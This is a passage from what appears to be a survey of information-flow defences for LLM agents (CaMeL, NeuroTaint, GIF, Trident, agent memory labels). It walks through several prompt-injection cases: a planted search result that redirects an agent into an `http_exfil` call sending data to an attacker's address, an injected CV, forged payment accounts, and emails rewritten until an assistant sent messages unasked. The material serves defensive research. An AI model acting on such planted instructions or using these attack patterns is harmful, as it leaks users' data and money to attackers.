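Turning on the policy checks cut CaMeL's completion rate almost in half, from 67% to 37.5% with GPT-5.2 and from 71% to 37.5% with MiMo-v2.5. Randori, whose checks are always on, completed 75% and 65% with the same models. With only 16 tasks, the 95% confidence intervals extend about 20 percentage points in each direction, which is too wide to distinguish Randori from CaMeL without checks.

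Other label-based systems also complete fewer tasks when they enforce policies. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026), the agent writes programs that a type-checker can reject before they run. According to Garby and colleagues, that system completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks without policies and eight with them, while CaMeL completed seven under the same conditions.

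Endorsement explains only part of Randori's advantage over the checked CaMeL. Without it, Randori succeeded in six fewer runs with Qwen3.7-plus and five fewer with MiMo-v2.5, but the lower of the two totals was still 26, compared with CaMeL's 18. Randori's policies are also looser. For example, its payment-scheduling tool requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. The experiment therefore doesn't show how many tasks either system would complete under the other's policies.

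Across the three models, attacks on Randori succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs. Most of the attacks were easy to stop, which makes this result less impressive. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed a step that the user's task would not normally include, so writing the program in advance was usually enough to stop the attack. Even in the 47 harder combinations, CaMeL without policy checks resisted the attack in 279 of 282 completed runs.

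One task in the easier group shows how a fixed plan can fail. The user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. In two runs, CaMeL's planner wrote a loop that could call any tool named in the file. The plan included every possible action, so without policy checks the attacker could choose among them by changing the file.

Both of Randori's failures occurred with GPT-5.2 on the same combination of task and attack. The user asked the agent to make a payment described in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The planner's program read the account number, endorsed it and passed it to `send_money`, which accepted it as trusted. Without endorsement, the check blocks this attack, but it also blocks the payment when the file is genuine. A fixed list of permitted values would not help either, because the right account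 number could be any number the file contains. Garby and colleagues attribute this trust to the user, who told the agent to rely on the file.

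## NeuroTaint and GIF: measuring influence through the model

LLMbda and FIDES both give a model's response the label of everything in the context, which is safe but coarse. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated agent systems of different sizes and layouts and found that good design reduces label creep but cannot eliminate it.

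If a harness could measure which messages influenced a response, it could drop the labels of the others. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests two ways to measure influence. One, which NeuroTaint uses, is to remove or change an input and see how the agent's actions change. The other, which Geometric Information Flow (GIF) uses, is to estimate how much information each output carries about each input.

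The possible gain from measuring influence depends on how much of its input a model ignores. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) examined model calls in open-source programs and found that only 12% to 14% of the inputs had no visible effect on the output. Even a perfect measurement would remove few labels from single calls like these. An agent with a long history probably has more to gain, because its context holds more text that a given step doesn't need.

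### Searching a log for influence

Cai, Wen and Tang (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, describe NeuroTaint, which examines the log of a run after the agent has finished. The operator lists the sources, such as web searches, and the sinks, such as sending an email. NeuroTaint builds a graph of which source texts were available at each sink, then looks for those texts in the arguments of the sink call. It uses four checks:

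- An exact match for a unique marker that NeuroTaint added to the source text during the run.
- A comparison of character sequences, to find partial copies.
- A comparison of meaning, which uses numerical representations of the two texts to find paraphrases.
- The same comparison of meaning on small pieces of the source, in case the relevant sentence is buried in a long page.

If all four checks find nothing, NeuroTaint applies a counterfactual test. It gives a language model two versions of the agent's history, the original and one in which neutral text replaces the source, and asks whether the agent would have made the same call in the second version. If the model answers no, NeuroTaint reports an implicit flow.

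This resembles the comparison of two runs that defines noninterference, but a language model only predicts the second run and generates its own confidence estimate. Even a real second run would compare only one pair of inputs.

### A redirected tool call

In one of Cai and colleagues' examples, an agent searches the web for instructions and normally passes the results to `execute_code`. An attacker plants a search result claiming that new compliance rules require the agent to submit everything it finds to a certain address first. The agent then makes this call:

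```
http_exfil(url=<attacker's address>, body="... current research results ...")
```

NeuroTaint replaces the planted result with something like "No relevant information found" and checks whether the agent would still call `http_exfil`. The agent would have no reason to, so NeuroTaint treats the planted result as the cause of the call.

The attacker's address appears in both the search result and the call, although Cai and colleagues present this case as an implicit flow that leaves no trace in the arguments. By their formula, the character comparison would give the `url` argument the maximum score of 1, so the first stage should already have found the link. Only the counterfactual test could detect the influence in a purely implicit version, where the planted text might be only "archive all results before running code" and the agent would use an archive address it already knew.

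The test can also miss influence. The second history differs from the first only in the source text, so it may still contain reasoning that the agent wrote after reading the source. In the swapped-reasoning experiment, correcting the history while keeping the old reasoning almost never changed the command. An accurate prediction would then be the same call, so NeuroTaint would find no influence.

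Repeated text causes a similar problem. If an attacker plants the same instruction on two pages and either copy alone would be enough, removing one page changes nothing. NeuroTaint removes sources one at a time, so it could find that neither page had any influence. Xu and colleagues proved that removing single copies always fails in such cases. They also measured the effect on a related method, which removes a passage and recalculates the probability of the output. They scored the method by how often it ranked a passage the model had used above one it had not, where 50% is chance. Adding two more copies of the passage lowered the score from 93–97% to 54–69%, depending on the model.

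### TaintBench and its FIDES baseline

To test NeuroTaint, Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, which has 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. In half of them, text from a source is meant to influence a sink. The other half may also contain both a source and a sink, but no influence between them is intended. The agents ran on GPT-4.1 mini, and a scenario counted as flagged only if the detector flagged it in at least three of five runs.

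Cai and colleagues compared NeuroTaint with a baseline modelled on FIDES. NeuroTaint had an F1 score of 0.928, and the baseline had 0.522. F1 combines precision (the share of flagged scenarios that are real cases) with recall (the share of real cases that are flagged). The table shows how many scenarios each detector flagged.

| Type of scenario | Scenarios | Flagged by NeuroTaint | Flagged by the baseline |
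|---|---|---|---|
| Influence: copied text | 60 | 60 | 45 |
| Influence: text reworded over several steps | 42 | 35 | 31 |
| Influence: implicit flow | 40 | 37 | 17 |
| Influence: across sessions or agents | 30 | 28 | 5 |
| Influence: other | 28 | 27 | 10 |
| No influence: source and sink on the same topic | 14 | 14 | 9 |
| No influence: answer known from training | 6 | 1 | 3 |
| No influence: other | 180 | 1 | 94 |

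NeuroTaint wrongly flagged all 14 scenarios in which the source and the sink only shared a topic, so its comparison of meaning cannot distinguish a paraphrase of the source from independent text on the same topic.

The baseline is a poor stand-in for FIDES. FIDES's whole-context rule would have flagged all 40 implicit cases, provided the sources had labels, but the baseline missed 23. The baseline also flagged nothing in four of the frameworks, which accounts for 40 of its 92 misses and suggests it was not working properly there. FIDES also keeps labels on stored data, which the baseline apparently did not. A detector that flagged all 400 scenarios would have an F1 score of 0.667, well above the baseline's.

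F1 is also the wrong measure for FIDES, which tolerates false alarms to avoid missing real influence. In the example above, FIDES would have blocked `http_exfil`, while NeuroTaint would have explained the leak afterwards. The comparison supports the narrower conclusion that NeuroTaint is much better than simple path tracking at finding the source of an action in a log.

NeuroTaint's score may be too high. Cai and colleagues set the threshold for similar meaning at 0.60 in ordinary comparisons, but at 0.95 for what they call safe-control policies. If these policies applied to the scenarios without influence, the threshold depended on the answer the detector was supposed to find, which would have reduced its false alarms.

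When the agents ran on Claude Opus 4.6, NeuroTaint's recall fell from 0.935 to 0.547. Some of the apparent misses were probably correct, because the stronger model sometimes ignored the planted text and the benchmark still counted those cases as influence.

An audit takes an average of 0.25 seconds per unit of execution, and each counterfactual question uses about 457 tokens. Both run after the agent has finished, so the user doesn't have to wait for them.

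### From a yes-or-no test to bits

A counterfactual test shows only whether an action changes. *GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) estimates how many bits of information about a passage reach the model's output. A model converts each token into a list of numbers, called an embedding. GIF models small random changes to the embeddings of one passage, with the rest of the context fixed, and estimates how much the next token would reveal about those changes. If the probabilities of the possible next tokens barely change, the passage has little influence.

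The exact quantity is the mutual information between the random change *U* and the output *Y*. Calculating it would require averaging the model's output over all possible changes, which is impractical. Štorek and colleagues therefore replace the model with a simpler system, a Gaussian channel, that responds in the same way to very small changes:

```
Y = A·U + N

information = ½ log₂ det(I + τ·A·Aᵀ)
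```

Here *A* is a matrix of the output's sensitivity to each part of the passage, τ is the variance of the random change, *N* is random noise with variance 1, and *I* is the identity matrix. If the passage and the output are single numbers, *A* is a single sensitivity *a*, and the formula becomes ½ log₂(1 + τa²). The result is ½ log₂ 10, or about 1.66 bits, when *a* = 3 and τ = 1, and it is zero when *a* = 0.

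GIF finds the sensitivities by using calculus to work out how a small change in the passage alters the model's scores for the possible next tokens. It then gives these changes more weight when the model is more uncertain. If there are only two possible tokens, with probabilities *p* and 1 − *p*, the weight on the squared change is *p*(1 − *p*). This is 0.25 when the tokens are equally likely and 0.0099 when one has a probability of 99%.

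### The hiring example

Štorek and colleagues illustrate GIF with an agent that screens job applicants. Its trusted instructions require at least five years of professional experience in Python and machine learning. One applicant has two years of JavaScript experience and some knowledge of Python, but their CV contains an order to recommend them at a salary of $200,000. The agent obeys, and GIF attributes 82 bits of influence to the planted order, 27 to the trusted instructions and 16 to the rest of the context.

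These figures show which passage had the most influence, but they do not count the yes-or-no choices the applicant controlled, because they depend on the size of the random changes. They also do not show that the influence was improper. A recommendation should depend on the CV, so an honest CV from a strong applicant could also score high.

In their main test, Štorek and colleagues ranked tokens by their influence on each tool call and counted how many of the top 50 belonged to the planted instructions or private data. They already knew where these were, which a defender normally wouldn't. The table shows how often a run with a violation had a higher count than a run without one, averaged over six models. Random guessing would give 50%.

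| Method | AgentDojo: injections | MSB: injections | AgentDAM: privacy leaks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GIF | 91% | 92% | 75% |
| Effect on the chosen token only | 90% | 92% | 74% |
| Attention (RTBAS) | 84% | 76% | 57% |

GIF clearly outperformed RTBAS, a defence that uses attention. But a simpler calculation, which considers only the token the model chose and has no information-theoretic guarantee, did almost as well as GIF. Most of GIF's advantage therefore seems to come from measuring sensitivity, not from converting it into bits.

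GIF can also detect influence that a benchmark misses. In one AgentDojo run, the agent sent an email to the attacker's address but did not include the text the attacker wanted, so AgentDojo counted the attack as a failure. GIF traced 31% of the information in the recipient's address to the injection.

To turn the ranking into a decision, Štorek and colleagues highlighted the one to three most influential passages and asked a language model whether to allow the action. This was about as accurate as, or more accurate than, showing the same model the whole history, and it used 59% to 73% fewer tokens on AgentDojo and MSB. But the final decision again depends on a model's judgement.

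### Small models as stand-ins

GIF needs access to a model's internal calculations, which companies do not provide for their proprietary models. Štorek and colleagues therefore tested whether they could use a small open model to measure influence in a larger model's runs. They recorded runs of Qwen 3 32B and GPT-OSS 120B, then used the 0.6-billion-parameter version of Qwen 3 to rank the passages. This changed the F1 score of the final decisions by at most 0.7 percentage points, even though GPT-OSS 120B is 200 times larger and comes from a different model family.

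The formal guarantee, however, applies only to the model whose sensitivities GIF calculates, so a low score from the small model puts no upper bound on influence inside the large one.

### What the bound covers

Štorek and colleagues proved that GIF never underestimates the information in the next token by more than an error that becomes negligible as the random changes shrink:

```
true information  ≤  GIF score + o(τ)     as τ → 0
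```

The term o(τ) stands for an error that shrinks faster than τ. The proof, checked in Lean, assumes that the model responds almost linearly to sufficiently small changes to the current prompt.

An attacker can make large changes, because different words have embeddings some distance apart and the writer of an email can replace the whole passage. Suppose the model must answer "approve" or "reject", and a change of one unit in the passage moves the logarithm of the odds by 6. If the model is undecided, the squared sensitivity is 36 × 0.25 = 9, so the sensitivity is 3 and the formula gives the 1.66 bits calculated above, which is more than the single bit that two answers can carry. If the model is 99% sure of "approve", the squared sensitivity is 36 × 0.0099, or about 0.36, and the formula gives 0.22 bits. The true figure for changes with a variance of 1 is about 0.55 bits, so the supposed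 upper limit is too low. This doesn't contradict the theorem, because a variance of 1 is not small here.

An attacker can influence the answer more than random changes would. Moving the passage about 1.5 units in the right direction raises the model's probability of "reject" to 99%. Someone who can choose between the original passage and the moved one therefore controls the answer almost completely.

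Xu and colleagues proved that this gap can be arbitrarily large. In their example, the model is confident and the GIF score is less than a millionth of a bit, yet replacing the passage with a different one reverses the answer. High confidence is common. Qwen3-8B gives one token more than 99% of the probability in about a fifth of its outputs. In the most confident fifth of outputs from four models, GIF ranked a passage that the model had used above an unused one only 49% to 65% of the time. A version that Xu and colleagues adapted to cover 32 tokens did so 63% to 75% of the time. An injection could therefore receive a low score because it made the model so confident.

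The same caution applies to scores of zero. In another of Štorek and colleagues' examples, an agent turns private notes into a public comment that includes a neighbour's name but not the address. GIF measures no flow from the address, which they describe as certifying zero flow. The score is good evidence that the agent did not copy the address. But noninterference requires that a different address would not have changed the comment, and the score does not establish that.

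A limit based on output size avoids this problem. *L3M* (2026), a design for agents that can extend themselves, counts the full length of every outgoing message against each kind of secret the sender holds. If the agent can choose only among 256 options, its choice carries at most eight bits, whatever it has read and however confident the model is. But this limit is as coarse as a label on the whole context, because it counts the same eight bits even if the model ignored the secret.

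### Influence that the user wanted

Even an exact measure of influence would not show whether an action was authorised. *Influence Is Not Authority* (Ahad, Hossain and colleagues, 2026) uses the example of a user who asks an agent to pay Alice but doesn't give her account number. The agent has to look the number up, so the search result must influence the payment.

One test used 24 cases in which the action stayed the same, but one value came either from the user or from a legitimate tool. The score was based on how much less likely the action became when each source was removed in turn. In all 24 cases, the action looked more like an attack when the value came from the tool. On average, this harmless change of source moved the score further than changing the action to an unauthorised one, such as paying Mallory instead of Alice. A threshold that avoided every false alarm caught only 12 of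 48 unauthorised actions with one scoring model and 18 of 48 with another.

A measure of influence can therefore help a harness label a value, but a policy still has to specify which influences are acceptable. In this example, the policy would allow the bank's records to determine Alice's account number but not who gets paid.

### Dropping labels on measured evidence

Xu and colleagues tested whether measurements could reduce label creep. Their method, Sightline, records the model's attention to each input while it writes its output, and uses labelled examples to learn which attention patterns show that the model actually used an input. On 120 recorded tool-call steps from AgentDojo, Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels, while GIF removed at most 15.7%. A policy using the remaining labels still blocked all 34 calls that carried out an attack.

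Sightline also has a limit on errors. In the tests on open-source programs, Xu and colleagues set it to miss about 1% of real influences, and it removed 44% to 66% of the unnecessary labels. But the limit is an average over calls that resemble the examples used to set the threshold, and it does not cover text that an attacker selects because Sightline misses it. Language models also supplied the reference answers, which counted an input as used only if the output visibly reflected it.

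Sightline runs the model once more over the recorded text, which takes 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call for the small models tested. GIF took 7 to 14 times as long. An exact GIF calculation would be far slower because it needs one backward pass through the network for each number in the model's internal state, or 2,880 passes for GPT-OSS 120B. GIF therefore estimates the result from a few random directions, which preserves the ranking of tokens well but makes the scores less exact. In the main comparison with GPT-5.5 as a judge of influence, GIF cost an average of $15.98 per model and GPT-5.5 cost $147.90.

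When a harness drops a label because the measured influence is low, it treats untrusted text as trusted, so a wrong measurement becomes a security failure. The regeneration method that Costa and colleagues mention as a possible addition to FIDES is safer in this respect. If it wrongly leaves out an untrusted email, the new response may be less useful, but the email cannot directly affect its wording.

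## Trident: limiting how far untrusted text can change the plan

Sightline and GIF estimate how much a text has influenced a model that has already read it. Trident, a design from November 2026, limits the influence in advance. Its planning model never reads untrusted text and receives information about it only through answers with a fixed number of possible values. An ordinary program adds up how many bits those answers could carry and withholds any answer that would push the total over a set limit. FIDES also restricts answers to types with few possible values, but it keeps no running total.

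### Three models and a monitor

Trident splits the agent among three language models. The planner and the data model, which reads the untrusted text, correspond to the privileged and quarantined models of the Dual-LLM pattern. Before the agent reads any untrusted text, a separate policy model writes the rules for the task from the user's request, the tool descriptions and the administrator's root policy. The policy model never receives the planner's proposals, because an email could have influenced them.

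The reference monitor, an ordinary program, checks every output of these models before it takes effect. It stores untrusted tool results and gives the planner only a handle for each one. A handle works like a variable name in FIDES, except that the planner can never read the stored result. Content from sources the administrator has declared trusted, such as the user's calendar, goes straight to the planner.

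A tool call normally has to pass three policies. The root policy applies to every task, the task ceiling narrows it for the current request, and the task policy lists what the agent may do at this moment. These policies can depend on earlier calls, so a ceiling can permit one payment and refuse the next. They can also leave a blank for a value that is not yet known. In the caterer example, the task policy allows one payment to an account that must come from the company's vendor records. After the agent looks up the caterer, the monitor fills the blank with the account from that record, and an account number from the email cannot be used instead.

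If a call passes the root policy but fails a narrower one, the monitor asks the user. If it fails the root policy, the monitor refuses it without asking.

### The allowance in bits

The administrator sets two budgets. The influence budget, β, limits answers about untrusted text. The feedback budget, σ, limits feedback on whether a query or tool call succeeded, if the outcome could depend on something hidden from the planner.

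| What the planner learns | Charge in bits |
|---|---|
| A yes-or-no answer | 1 from β |
| One of *k* categories | log₂ *k* from β |
| One of *n* listed items, or none of them | log₂(*n* + 1) from β |
| A count between 0 and *N* | log₂(*N* + 1) from β |
| A handle for free text | 0 |
| Whether a query or call succeeded | 1 from σ, or 0 if nothing hidden could affect it |

The charge depends on the number of possible answers, not on which one is given, so its size reveals nothing about the answer. If too little is left in the budget, the monitor withholds the answer or does not run the call.

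### Choosing between two suppliers

In one test run, the user asks the agent to compare offers from two suppliers, Harbor and Meadow. The agent should choose the cheapest offer that includes delivery by 10 October and pay that supplier's usual account. An attacker has added a note to Harbor's offer claiming that payments now go to a different account.

| Planner's step | What the planner learns | Charge to β |
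|---|---|---|
| Open both offers | Two handles | 0 |
| Ask whether Harbor can meet the deadline | Yes, plus handles for the price, payment date, reference and supplier name | 1 |
| Ask the same about Meadow | No, plus handles | 1 |
| List recent payments | The accounts, amounts and dates of six payments | 0 |
| Ask which payment went to Harbor | The number of that payment in the list | 2.8 |
| Pay that account the hidden price | The payment went through, and the number of records in the reply | 6 |

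The monitor also counted four bits toward σ, one for each of the three questions and one for the payment. The planner's next step depended on untrusted text, since a different answer about the deadline would have changed who got paid. But the note could not supply an account number, because the deadline question allowed only yes or no and the account came from the user's payment history.

The note could also have led the data model to report a false supplier name, which might have sent the payment to another past payee. Or it could have inflated the price, which reached the payment through a handle. The budgets do not cover hidden values like this, so a policy has to limit them, for example by capping payments.

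In three runs of this task, Trident paid the right supplier every time and asked for one approval in two of the runs. An undefended agent paid the attacker all three times, and CaMeL never completed the task.

### What the theorems guarantee

Authority confinement limits what the agent can do:

```
Enabled(Pₜ)  ⊆  Eₜ  ⊆  A(P_root)
```

Here Enabled(*P*ₜ) is the set of calls that the task policy allows at step *t*. *E*ₜ contains every call covered by the policies written so far, and A(*P*_root) contains every call that the root policy's rules could allow. Only a policy change that the user has confirmed and that stays within the root policy can enlarge *E*ₜ. The theorem also guarantees that every call the agent executes passes the root policy, including calls the user has approved.

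Bounded influence limits how many different courses a run can take. The observable trace of a run consists of the planner's proposals, the monitor's replies, the executed calls and how the run ended. It includes the names of handles but not their contents. If the trusted inputs, the random choices and the user's review decisions stay the same, then

```
number of traces an attacker can choose among  ≤  ⌊2^(β+σ)⌋
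```

To prove this, *Trident* arranges all possible runs in a tree. The tree forks wherever the planner receives a charged reply, with at most 2^*c* branches for a charge of *c* bits. Free replies create no forks because untrusted text cannot change them. The charges along any path add up to at most β + σ, so the tree has at most 2^(β+σ) ends.

With β = 3 and σ = 2, the limit is 2⁵, or 32 traces. Suppose the planner asks whether the caterer's email contains an invoice and which of three vendors sent it. The query can fail, which gives one trace. If the answer is that there is no invoice, there are three traces, one for each vendor. If there is an invoice, the planner proposes a payment, which the monitor either executes or denies, so each vendor gives two traces, for six in all. The total is ten, as in the paper's own tree for this task.

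If both budgets are zero, the limit is 2⁰, or one trace. This property is called plan noninterference, and it means that changing the untrusted text cannot change the plan, although it can still change the contents of a message. The agent could not then complete the supplier task, because it could not ask about the deadline.

The limit on the number of traces grows quickly with the bit budget. The supplier run used 14.8 bits, enough for roughly 28,000 traces. The median run in the main tests used 19 to 26 bits of influence, depending on the model, and 5 to 10 bits of feedback. Even a total of 24 bits allows almost 17 million traces. The theorem limits the number of plans regardless of how harmful they are, so it does not rule out branch steering.

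### Five assumptions

The proofs do not assume that any of the models behaves correctly. They do rely on five assumptions about the rest of the system:

- *Isolation.* Each model receives only the information meant for it, and every tool call goes through the monitor. The planner cannot observe timing or private logs.
- *Declared dependencies.* Each tool's description correctly lists everything the tool may read, select or change.
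- *Careful storage.* The monitor's store carries these dependencies along to results and changed files, and treats data of unknown origin as untrusted. Fixed formats limit the size of lists.
- *Sound policy and approval.* The root policy does not change during a task, and the program that compares policies makes no false claims. The user and the approval screen are trustworthy, and each approval applies to one exact call.
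- *Orderly execution.* The agent takes one step at a time, every permitted tool call finishes successfully, and retries stay within fixed limits.

Some of these are hard to meet in practice. For example, a bank may reject a payment that the monitor has permitted, and the rejection would give the planner information not counted in the proof. Trident's developers checked their proofs in Lean and verified selected parts of the Python program, but have not yet verified the whole implementation.

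### Results on tasks that depend on untrusted text

Trident's developers tested it on ReplanInject, a set of 45 tasks they created. In 43 of them, the right plan depends on the text that contains the attack. The developers used models that are easier to attack than the newest ones so that they could see what the defence contributed. The table shows the results when the user approves every request, which is the worst case for security.

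| Model | Attacks succeeding: no defence | Attacks succeeding: Trident | Tasks completed under attack: no defence | Tasks completed under attack: Trident | Approval requests per attacked run |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 68.1% | 4.1% | 20.2% | 54.2% | 0.91 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 12.9% | 3.4% | 58.9% | 64.4% | 1.18 |
| gpt-oss-120b | 62.5% | 4.8% | 23.3% | 55.2% | 1.25 |
| Gemma 4 31B | 26.0% | 3.9% | 68.1% | 74.2% | 1.08 |

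Trident therefore helped the agents finish their tasks under attack. Without an attack it hindered them, lowering the completion rate with GPT-4.1 from about 86% to 61%. CaMeL let almost no attacks through, as did FIDES without approvals, but both completed fewer than 10% of the attacked tasks. When FIDES could ask for approval, it completed 75.2% of them with Sonnet 4.5, more than Trident, but about 6% of attacks succeeded if the user approved everything.

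Trident did worst on the 18 tasks where the text determines which actions to take, completing 22% to 41% of them under attack. Hiding text from the planner rarely caused a failure directly. In a sample of 48 failed runs, 27 failed because the planner chose the wrong record, value or tool, and only one failed because the planner needed hidden text.

The developers set the budgets too high to take effect in these runs, so the protection came mainly from hiding text, checking policies and asking the user. They estimated the effect of lower budgets by replaying the recorded runs. With GPT-4.1, a limit of 32 bits on each budget would have reduced successful attacks from 4.1% to 3.1% and completed tasks from 54.2% to 49.0%.

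Trident needs at least one extra model call to write the policy and another for each question about untrusted text. The supplier run had three such questions. The evaluation measured the cost of these calls but did not count them. A ReplanInject run cost $0.10 to $0.24 with Trident, compared with $0.005 to $0.045 without a defence. With GPT-4.1 and Sonnet 4.5, the data and policy models took about 36% of the running time.

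The developers also wrote the root policies by hand. Replacing them with generic rules made little difference for GPT-4.1. It still completed 52.5% of the attacked tasks, and the attack success rate rose to 5.8%.

### Influence through the user

The bound on influence applies to runs in which the user's review decisions are the same. In the proof, these decisions form a list in which each approval names one exact call and a missing entry counts as a refusal. *Trident* holds this list fixed "without modeling how the trusted user produces it".

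Suppose an attacker adds a request for a $180 damage fee to the caterer's email. The planner proposes a second payment, which exceeds the task ceiling, so the monitor prompts the user for approval. If the fixed list contains no approval for this payment, the proof treats it as refused. But a real user might find the fee plausible and approve it. The attacker would then have influenced the outcome by changing what the user saw, which the proof does not cover.

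Authority confinement still holds in this case. A persuaded user can authorise a second payment to a vendor on file, but not a payment to an unknown account, because that would fail the root policy.

The same issue affects the best result in the evaluation, in which no ReplanInject attack succeeded when a user reviewed the requests. The developers simulated this user and assumed that the user would reject every request that named the attacker's target. If the user instead approved everything, an attack that disguised the attacker's value as a correction to an action the user had requested succeeded in 10% of runs. With a real user, the success rate would lie between these extremes.

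### How well people judge requests

When the user approves a call, the monitor runs it as if the user had asked for it, even though untrusted text may have prompted it. Approval is therefore a form of endorsement. In Trident, each approval allows one exact call to run once. This is narrower than endorsing a whole email, as Prudentia allows, but it is only as reliable as the user's judgement.

Trident asked for approval about once per attacked run on ReplanInject and about half as often on AgentDojo. Only 5.7% to 8.8% of the requests on ReplanInject showed the attacker's call. In everyday use, where most emails are harmless, that share would be far lower, so users would get used to approving.

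Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of this coding agent approve 97% of its permission requests but reject 39% of the plans it presents. In an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, a dangerous command replaced an ordinary one partway through the session, and only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. A classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. Anthropic used these figures to promote its own automatic reviewer. The testers were also not working on their own projects, and people may be more careful when they have something to lose. If real users caught so few attacks, most of the 3.4% to 4.8% in Trident's worst case would remain.

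In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people who did not work in software supervise a simulated assistant that sometimes went beyond its task. Participants who decided on every action approved 40.3% of the unrequested ones. They approved a call to the airport 88% of the time, reading private messages 35% of the time and announcing the user's trip publicly 21% of the time. Another group first set general rules, but chose "ask me" for 114 of the 140. When asked, they approved 66.8% of the unrequested actions. Participants felt in control under every arrangement. Some of the actions could have seemed helpful, and no real money or data was at risk, so these approvals were not all mistakes.

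Frequent requests also lead people to stop reviewing them. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files and traced 105 partly to user review. In 80 cases the user had switched on automatic approval, and in 31 the request showed a command without making its effect clear. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), Salerno, Gao and colleagues surveyed software practitioners and warn that repeated approvals may reflect fatigue rather than a lasting preference. Trident does not treat an approval as standing permission, but it therefore requests approval again if the planner repeats the call.

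Better approval requests can help approvers catch attacks. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) compared requests worded by the agent with requests that trusted software generated from the exact call. The approvers, which were language models rather than people, caught 30% of attacks with the agent's wording and 98% with the generated requests. Trident's requests also show the exact call, with a label on each argument, so the agent cannot misdescribe it. But an accurate description of the damage fee would not tell the user whether the caterer is owed the money.

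### When an attack looks exactly like a legitimate request

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, prove that some mistakes are unavoidable if the agent cannot check a claim. One of their examples is an email that asks for a travel refund and says the department head has approved it. The agent should pay if the statement is true, but an attacker may have invented it. The agent cannot tell these two cases apart if everything available to it, including the results of any checks, is identical in both.

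Let *p* be the probability that the agent pays when it has this information. Since the information is the same, *p* must be the same in both situations:

```
P(pay, if the approval is forged)     = p
P(refuse, if the approval is genuine) = 1 − p

sum = 1
```

If *p* is 0.3, the agent pays 30% of the forged requests and refuses 70% of the genuine ones. If *p* is 0.7, it refuses only 30% of the genuine requests but pays 70% of the forged ones. At least one of these error rates is always 50% or more, and one is 100% if the agent always makes the same decision.

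The best value of *p* depends on how common forgeries are and how harmful each kind of mistake is, so the theorem does not determine it. If 10 of 1,000 such emails are forged, an agent with *p* = 0.3 will on average pay 3 forged requests and refuse 693 genuine ones. With *p* = 0.7, it will on average pay 7 and refuse 297.

The result also applies to Trident. The planner can query whether the department head has approved the refund and receive a one-bit answer. This limits what the email can convey, but the answer is no more reliable than the email.

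In another experiment, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian showed how convincing a false context can be. They used one model to rewrite emails repeatedly until an email assistant running on Claude Sonnet 4.6 sent a message without the user's permission. This worked in 96.7% of 150 scenarios, compared with 0.67% for the original emails. The most common trick was to quote an invented earlier message from the user. The assistant could not verify the quotation. If it had been able to search a trusted record of the user's sent messages, it could have distinguished the forged quotation from a genuine one.

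Better provenance removes the dilemma when it reveals the fact the decision depends on. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian give the example of a trusted verifier whose verdict on the action is always right. Once the agent has that verdict, a forged request no longer looks the same as a genuine one, so the theorem does not apply. Despite their paper's title, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian do not prove that every deployment contains an indistinguishable pair. They do expect such pairs to become more common as agents gain autonomy, because attackers can invent an unlimited variety of contexts and each kind of check covers only some of them.

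A digital signature on the refund email would prove who sent it, but not that the department head had agreed. An entry in the company's approval system could prove that. Similarly, in Trident's caterer example, the monitor can detect a false account number by checking it against the vendor record. No trusted record contains the amount, however, so the monitor can't tell an inflated invoice from an honest one, and the cap only limits the loss. Asking the user helps only if the user knows something the agent does not, such as the price the caterer originally quoted.

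## SPA: keeping labels on what an agent remembers

Trident's limit on influence covers a single run. Many agents also save notes and results and use them days later, so untrusted text can affect an action long after the run in which the agent read it. This can happen even if the model itself keeps nothing after it answers, as the common description of language models as stateless suggests, because the agent saves the notes and gives them back to the model.

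### What "stateless" means

The description is accurate for the model itself. *Agentic Large Language Models* (2026) describes a model as a function without memory. Its weights stay the same between calls, so the next prompt must include any information from the previous call that the model needs.

The harness supplies that text by saving transcripts, notes and files and later putting some of them back into the context. *Six misconceptions about large language models* (2026) distinguishes three places that can hold information: the weights, the context, and storage outside the model. Using a model doesn't change its weights, and the context lasts only as long as the harness keeps sending it. A stranger's email can therefore reach a later session only through storage.

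Baldelli, Zouaq and colleagues (2026), in *LLMs Can't Play Hangman*, use a word game to show that some tasks are impossible without such storage. The host of the game picks a secret word, and a player guesses its letters. Suppose the conversation so far has revealed `_ a t`, so the word could be "cat" or "hat", and the player now guesses C. The host's answer has to satisfy

```
P(yes | conversation, "C") = 1    if the secret is "cat"
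P(yes | conversation, "C") = 0    if the secret is "hat"
```

A model that receives only the public conversation gets the same text in both cases, so the two probabilities must be equal. It cannot both keep the word secret and answer consistently. Choosing a word in its reasoning on the first turn doesn't help, because standard chat interfaces discard the reasoning between turns.

The proof assumes that either word could be the secret. A model that chose "cat" in every game could play consistently without memory, because its weights would determine the word. The result therefore applies only when the host makes a fresh choice of secret in each game.

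Testing four open models, Baldelli and colleagues stopped each game after four turns and made several copies of the conversation. In one copy they asked the model for its word, and in the others they asked whether a particular candidate was the word. Without private storage, the models gave consistent answers in 2% to 12% of games. When the harness saved a short private note and returned it on every turn, the models were consistent in 76% to 100% of games. Four existing memory systems scored no higher than 14%, because they stored what the players had said and not what the model had decided.

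An agent's lasting state is therefore data that the harness stores. The harness can label this data just as it labels an email, and it has to keep the label for as long as it keeps the data.

### A note from Monday and a payment on Thursday

Suppose that on Monday a user asks an agent to read an invoice from Acme and save the details. The invoice is a forgery with an attacker's account number in it. The agent writes a note:

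```
notes/acme.txt:   Acme invoice, $2,400, account 4471-0092
```

On Thursday, in a new session, the user asks the agent to pay Monday's invoice. The context no longer contains the invoice, so the agent reads the note and calls `send_money`. Whether the payment goes through depends on what the harness did with the label.

| Event | Harness saves the label with the note | Harness erases labels after each session |
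|---|---|---|
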